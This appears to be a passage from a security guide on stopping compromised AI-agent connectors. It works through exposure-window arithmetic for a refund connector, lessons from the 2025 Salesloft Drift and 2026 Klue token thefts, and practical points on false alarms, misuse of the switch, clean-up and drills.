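The exposure window runs from the attacker's first use of a connector to the moment its authority is gone. It has three parts:

exposure window = detection + decision + propagation

Detection lasts until someone notices the attack, decision until someone orders the stop, and propagation until every service refuses the credential.

Suppose the shop needs 20 hours to notice false refunds, an hour to find someone with the authority to stop the connector, and an hour for the cancellation to reach all of the processor's servers. The attacker then has a 22-hour window. With the original key, the attacker can refund all $600,000 in the first 25 minutes, but the caps limit the loss to $15,000 over the whole window.

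A careful attacker might spread the capped refunds over the day, at $625 an hour, to avoid notice. The table compares that attacker with one who uses the unrestricted key at full speed.

| Detection | Decision | Propagation | Window | Unrestricted key | Capped key, steady theft |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 20 hours | 1 hour | 1 hour | 22 hours | $600,000 | $13,750 |
| 20 hours | 1 hour | None | 21 hours | $600,000 | $13,125 |
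| 20 hours | None | None | 20 hours | $600,000 | $12,500 |
| 1 hour | 1 hour | 1 hour | 3 hours | $600,000 | $1,875 |

A switch that takes effect the instant someone notices the attack saves $1,250. Noticing the attack after one hour instead of 20 saves almost ten times as much, even with the slow switch. If the attacker uses up the capped allowance at the start, a faster switch saves nothing on the first day.

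With the unrestricted key, none of the rows in the table makes a difference. At ten refunds a second the attacker takes $24,000 a minute, so to keep the loss to $15,000 the shop would have to notice, decide and cut off access within 38 seconds. Only an automatic control could act that fast, and a cap is simpler than an automatic cutoff.

The shop could detect most false refunds much sooner by comparing the processor's refunds with the requests in the host's log. Every refund should match a request for the same charge and amount. If a program outside the connector made this comparison every 15 minutes, it would find any refund that the model hadn't requested. The window would fall to about two and a quarter hours and the steady loss to about $1,400.

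The comparison wouldn't catch refunds that an injected prompt caused, because the model did request those. It also wouldn't catch a connector that only copies data, such as customer records, because no money goes missing. Such thefts have gone on for days.

### The Salesloft Drift theft

Salesloft's Drift chat tool held tokens that could read companies' records in the customer database Salesforce, so it was effectively a remote connector. An attacker stole those tokens in 2025.

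Google's investigators describe the thefts in Larsen, Lin and colleagues (2025), in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift*. The internet company Cloudflare (2025), one of the victims, published a log of what the attacker did in its account, and Clari/Salesloft's *Trust Center* covers the earlier break-in. Together they give this timeline, with times in UTC:

| Date in 2025 | Event |
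|---|---|
| March to June | The attacker uses Salesloft's GitHub account to download code, add a guest user and set up workflows |
| By early August | The attacker enters Drift's cloud systems and takes customers' tokens |
| 8 August | Earliest known thefts from customers' Salesforce accounts |
| 9 August | The attacker uses other Drift tokens to read email in a few Google Workspace accounts |
| 12 August, 22:14 | The attacker logs in to Cloudflare's Salesforce account |
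| 14 August | The attacker counts Cloudflare's records and looks up the limits on data requests |
| 17 August, 11:11 to 11:15 | The attacker exports the text of Cloudflare's support cases, then deletes the export job |
| 18 August | Latest thefts in Google's account |
| 20 August | Salesloft and Salesforce revoke all active access and refresh tokens for Drift |

The window for the Salesforce tokens was about 12 days, and detection took up nearly all of it. In its first notice, which Cloudflare dates to 20 August, Salesloft wrote that it had detected the problem that day and had already revoked the connections. Decision and propagation therefore took less than a day. The attacker had finished with Cloudflare three days before the notice, after an export that took under four minutes. The Hacker News (2025) reports that Google knew of more than 700 organisations that might be affected.

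If a compromise of the shop's capped refund connector went unnoticed for 12 days, an attacker could take about $180,000. Responding two hours faster would save about $1,250 of that.

Restricting the IP addresses from which a token can be used might have stopped the thefts even if no one had detected them. Salesloft later published the addresses that Drift uses and told partners to treat a login with a Drift token from any other address as suspicious. The attacker reached Cloudflare's records from rented servers that weren't on that list. If Cloudflare's Salesforce account had accepted the token only from Drift's addresses, those logins would have failed. However, an attacker inside Drift's own systems might have been able to send requests from those addresses.

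### What the revocation missed

The mass revocation on 20 August covered Drift's connection to Salesforce. Drift also held tokens for other services, including the email tokens that the attacker had used on 9 August. Google did not confirm the theft of those email tokens until 28 August, 19 days after the attacker used them. It then revoked the tokens and disabled the integration.

Salesloft could cancel OAuth tokens for all its customers at once by replacing the keys that identified Drift to other services. But some customers had connected Drift to a service by pasting in an API key, which only the customer could revoke, at that service. Salesloft could only ask these customers to revoke their keys, so cutting off this access depended on each customer reading the request and acting on it.

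Salesloft's first notice also asked administrators to reconnect Drift to Salesforce straight away. Reconnecting would have created new tokens in a system that nobody had fully investigated. The final investigation summary dates the intrusion from 22 March to 5 September, so the attacker may still have had some access when customers reconnected. The advice was risky, although Salesloft reported no sign of further thefts after the revocation.

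Salesforce removed that risk eight days later. According to Salesforce's status notices, it disabled Drift's connection at 04:09 UTC on 28 August, and all other Salesloft integrations later that day. This stop passes the independence test because the command went only through Salesforce, so it would have worked even if the attacker had controlled every system at Salesloft. It also kept customers from reconnecting before anyone had checked that Drift was safe.

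### Klue, ten months later

In a similar theft in June 2026, the attacker had much less time. Klue sells information about business competitors, and its Battlecards app connects to customers' Salesforce accounts. According to Klue's *CrowdStrike Investigation Summary* (2026), an attacker used a stolen GitHub token on 11 June to add code to the service that manages these connections, and the code collected customers' tokens. Salesforce alerted Klue on 12 June, and that same morning Klue shut down the affected servers, disabled the GitHub tokens and replaced its OAuth credentials.

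The window was about one day instead of 12 because the receiving service detected the breach. Klue acted quickly, but Salesloft had also done so once it knew. The *Cybersecurity Alert* from FINRA, which regulates the US brokerage industry, credits Klue with the detection. Klue's own account credits the receiving service, and is more believable because a company has little reason to give another the credit.

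A day was still long enough for the attacker to steal data. The Hacker News (2026) quotes an account that the attacker used the stolen tokens to query customers' records directly and copy them, and FINRA describes an extortion campaign against the victims.

The one-day figure may also be too low. Klue reports no sign of the attacker in its own environment after 12 June, but stolen tokens may have kept working elsewhere after that date. FINRA lists nine connected platforms, including Slack, Google Drive and Zoom. Salesforce disabled Klue's app on 17 June, five days after Klue replaced its credentials, but this blocked the app's access only to Salesforce.

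Datadog Security Labs cites the security company Huntress, which traced the break-in to a credential that Klue had made for a prototype and never cancelled. Klue's investigators couldn't establish how the attacker obtained the GitHub token. If Huntress is right, Klue could have revoked the credential months or years before the attack without interrupting anything.

### False alarms

People who fear the cost of shutting off an uncompromised connector will hesitate to do it. For the refund connector, that cost is small. Suppose the agent makes ten refunds an hour, and a staff member needs five minutes, or $2 of paid time, to make one by hand. A four-hour pause to investigate would then mean 40 manual refunds, costing $80.

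If the alarm is real, leaving the connector on for those four hours costs $2,500 at the steady capped rate, so pausing is worthwhile whenever the chance of a real attack is above 3.2%. With the unrestricted key, $600,000 is at risk and the threshold falls to one in 7,500. The cap therefore lets staff investigate a weak alarm before deciding whether to pause the connector.

These figures don't justify an automatic pause at every alarm. The best detector that King and colleagues trained flagged 2.6% of harmless sessions. With ten sessions an hour and a four-hour pause after each alarm, the shop's connector would be off for nearly half the working day, and almost every alarm would be false. A refund at the processor that matches no request in the host's log is much stronger evidence, and the shop could reasonably let that trigger a pause by itself.

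The joint guidance recommends rules that automatically restrict an agent's permissions when the agent behaves unexpectedly. The same approach suits a connector. The processor or broker could first lower the daily cap to ten refunds, which a person can undo in a minute. Revoking the token is harder to undo because someone has to authorize the connector again.

On a large platform, a wrong or overly broad stop can disrupt customers' work. When Salesforce disabled all Salesloft's integrations, only Drift had shown signs of an attack, and investigators later found only limited reconnaissance in Salesloft's main product. Customers of that product still lost their connection to Salesforce for almost ten days. Their sales activity didn't reach Salesforce, and their forecasts were out of date or unavailable.

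Salesforce's decision was still reasonable. On 28 August nobody had yet verified that Drift was properly separated from Salesloft's main systems, and on the same day Google found that the theft was wider than Salesloft had thought.

### Misuse of the switch

Anyone who can press the switch can stop the shop's refunds, so an attacker may want access to it too. A competitor, an extortionist or an angry former employee could turn the connector off during the busiest week of the year. An attacker could also set off false alarms until staff started to ignore them.

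The shop can limit this by separating the power to stop the connector from the power to restart it. A single staff member should be able to stop it at any hour, because delay helps an attacker, but restarting it should take two people. The login for the switch should give no other access, so that someone who steals it can interrupt refunds but can't issue any. The switch should log each use in a system that neither the connector nor its administrators can change.

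Requiring two people to stop the connector would prevent some misuse but slow the decision. If the second person takes three hours to answer the phone, another $1,875 could be lost through the capped connector.

Attackers can also exploit the reconnection step. After a mass revocation, customers expect a message asking them to log in and authorize the connection again, and a fake one would look much the same. Staff should reconnect from the service's own settings page and ignore links in email.

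### Half-finished actions

Stopping a connector can cause a duplicate refund. If staff shut it down after the processor has refunded a kettle but before the connector reports back, the agent may treat the request as failed and repeat it after the restart.

The shop should mark any request without a result as unknown and check it against the processor's records. It can also prevent most duplicate refunds by giving each refund a unique number, keeping that number the same when the host retries, and having the processor or broker reject any number it has already handled.

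Tasks with several steps are harder to repair. An agent that replaces a faulty kettle might cancel the old order, refund it, create a new order and email the customer. If staff stop it after the first step, the customer has neither a working kettle nor a refund. A list of completed steps, kept outside the connector, lets a person finish the task or reverse it. The joint guidance recommends having a way to roll an agent back to an earlier working version, but this restores only the software and can't recall an email or return money that a thief has spent.

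Cancelling a token doesn't necessarily stop jobs that were started with it. Many services let a program start a long job, such as an export, and collect the result later. Staff should look for unfinished jobs in the service's own records and stop them there.

Other agents may also keep running without detecting that a connector is missing. While Salesforce was disconnected, Salesloft told customers that its AI agents would continue to use data from the last sync. Old data is acceptable for a sales summary, but an agent that issued refunds from an outdated list of orders could refund some customers twice. Such an agent should stop when its data is too old.

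### Repairs after the stop

Cancelling the connector's token doesn't cancel the secrets an attacker found with it. The Drift attacker searched the stolen records for passwords, Amazon cloud keys and access tokens for the data service Snowflake. Each secret has its own exposure window, which starts when the attacker copies it.

Cloudflare's stolen support cases contained whatever customers had pasted into them. The company searched the stolen text with its own scanning tools and found 104 Cloudflare API tokens, which it replaced between 26 and 29 August. The attacker had taken the text on 17 August, so the tokens were exposed for nine to 12 days. Cloudflare saw no suspicious use of them, but it could replace only the secrets it had issued. On 2 September, it told customers to replace any other secrets they had shared in a support case.

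Cloudflare also disabled the Drift user account, removed all Salesloft software and disconnected every other outside service from Salesforce. It then reconnected the services one at a time with new credentials and stricter controls, and began replacing those credentials every week. This was far more work than turning off one connector, but it was justified because the attacker had spent days in the account and might have found a way into the other services.

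An attacker may leave behind access that still works after the key is replaced. The Drift attacker added a guest user to Salesloft's GitHub account. An attacker could also create a forwarding rule in a mailbox or a second API key at a payment processor. The shop should check the service's records, not the connector's, for users, keys and rules created since the attack began.

Those records also have to survive the clean-up. Cloudflare could reconstruct the export even though the attacker had deleted the job, because other logs remained. If the shop deletes a malicious connector straight away, it may lose the best evidence of what the attacker took. It is better to cancel the key first, then disconnect the machine and keep a copy of it.

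After a stop, the two systems that the connector linked may hold different data. Salesloft and Salesforce ran separately for almost ten days, and Salesloft's staff had to help each customer reconcile the data before the sync could resume. The shop would likewise have to reconcile any refunds that staff made by hand during the pause.

The connector should go back online only with new credentials, and only after someone has closed the path the attacker used. Salesforce restored the other Salesloft integrations on 7 September, after the security company Mandiant had checked Salesloft's repairs, but Drift stayed disconnected.

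### Drills

An organization that has never used its kill switch doesn't know how long it takes to work. The joint guidance recommends testing incident response plans regularly, but it sets no target for how quickly a stop should work.

To measure propagation delay, the shop can copy a test key to a computer outside its network and have that computer use the key to look up an old order every ten seconds. A staff member then cancels the key, and the delay is the time until the first refusal. The test uses an outside computer because shutting down the connector would stop the connector's own requests even if the key still worked. The shop should repeat the test with the host switched off to check that the kill switch works without it.

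To measure detection time, a manager can use the connector's key to issue a $1 refund with no matching ticket, tell nobody, and time how long it takes someone to notice. This is probably the longest of the three times and the most useful to know. Running the drill late on a Saturday also shows how long the shop needs to find someone who can order a stop.

A drill should also check that staff can find everything they need to cancel. Salesloft told Drift customers to look up their connected services in Drift's settings and revoke the API keys at each one. On 5 September it took Drift offline, which made those settings unavailable, but it still advised customers to revoke the keys. Any customer who hadn't copied the list by then had to rebuild it from memory or from the other services' records. The shop should keep its own list of connectors somewhere that stays available when they are off,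 showing the credentials each connector holds, where to cancel them and who can do it.
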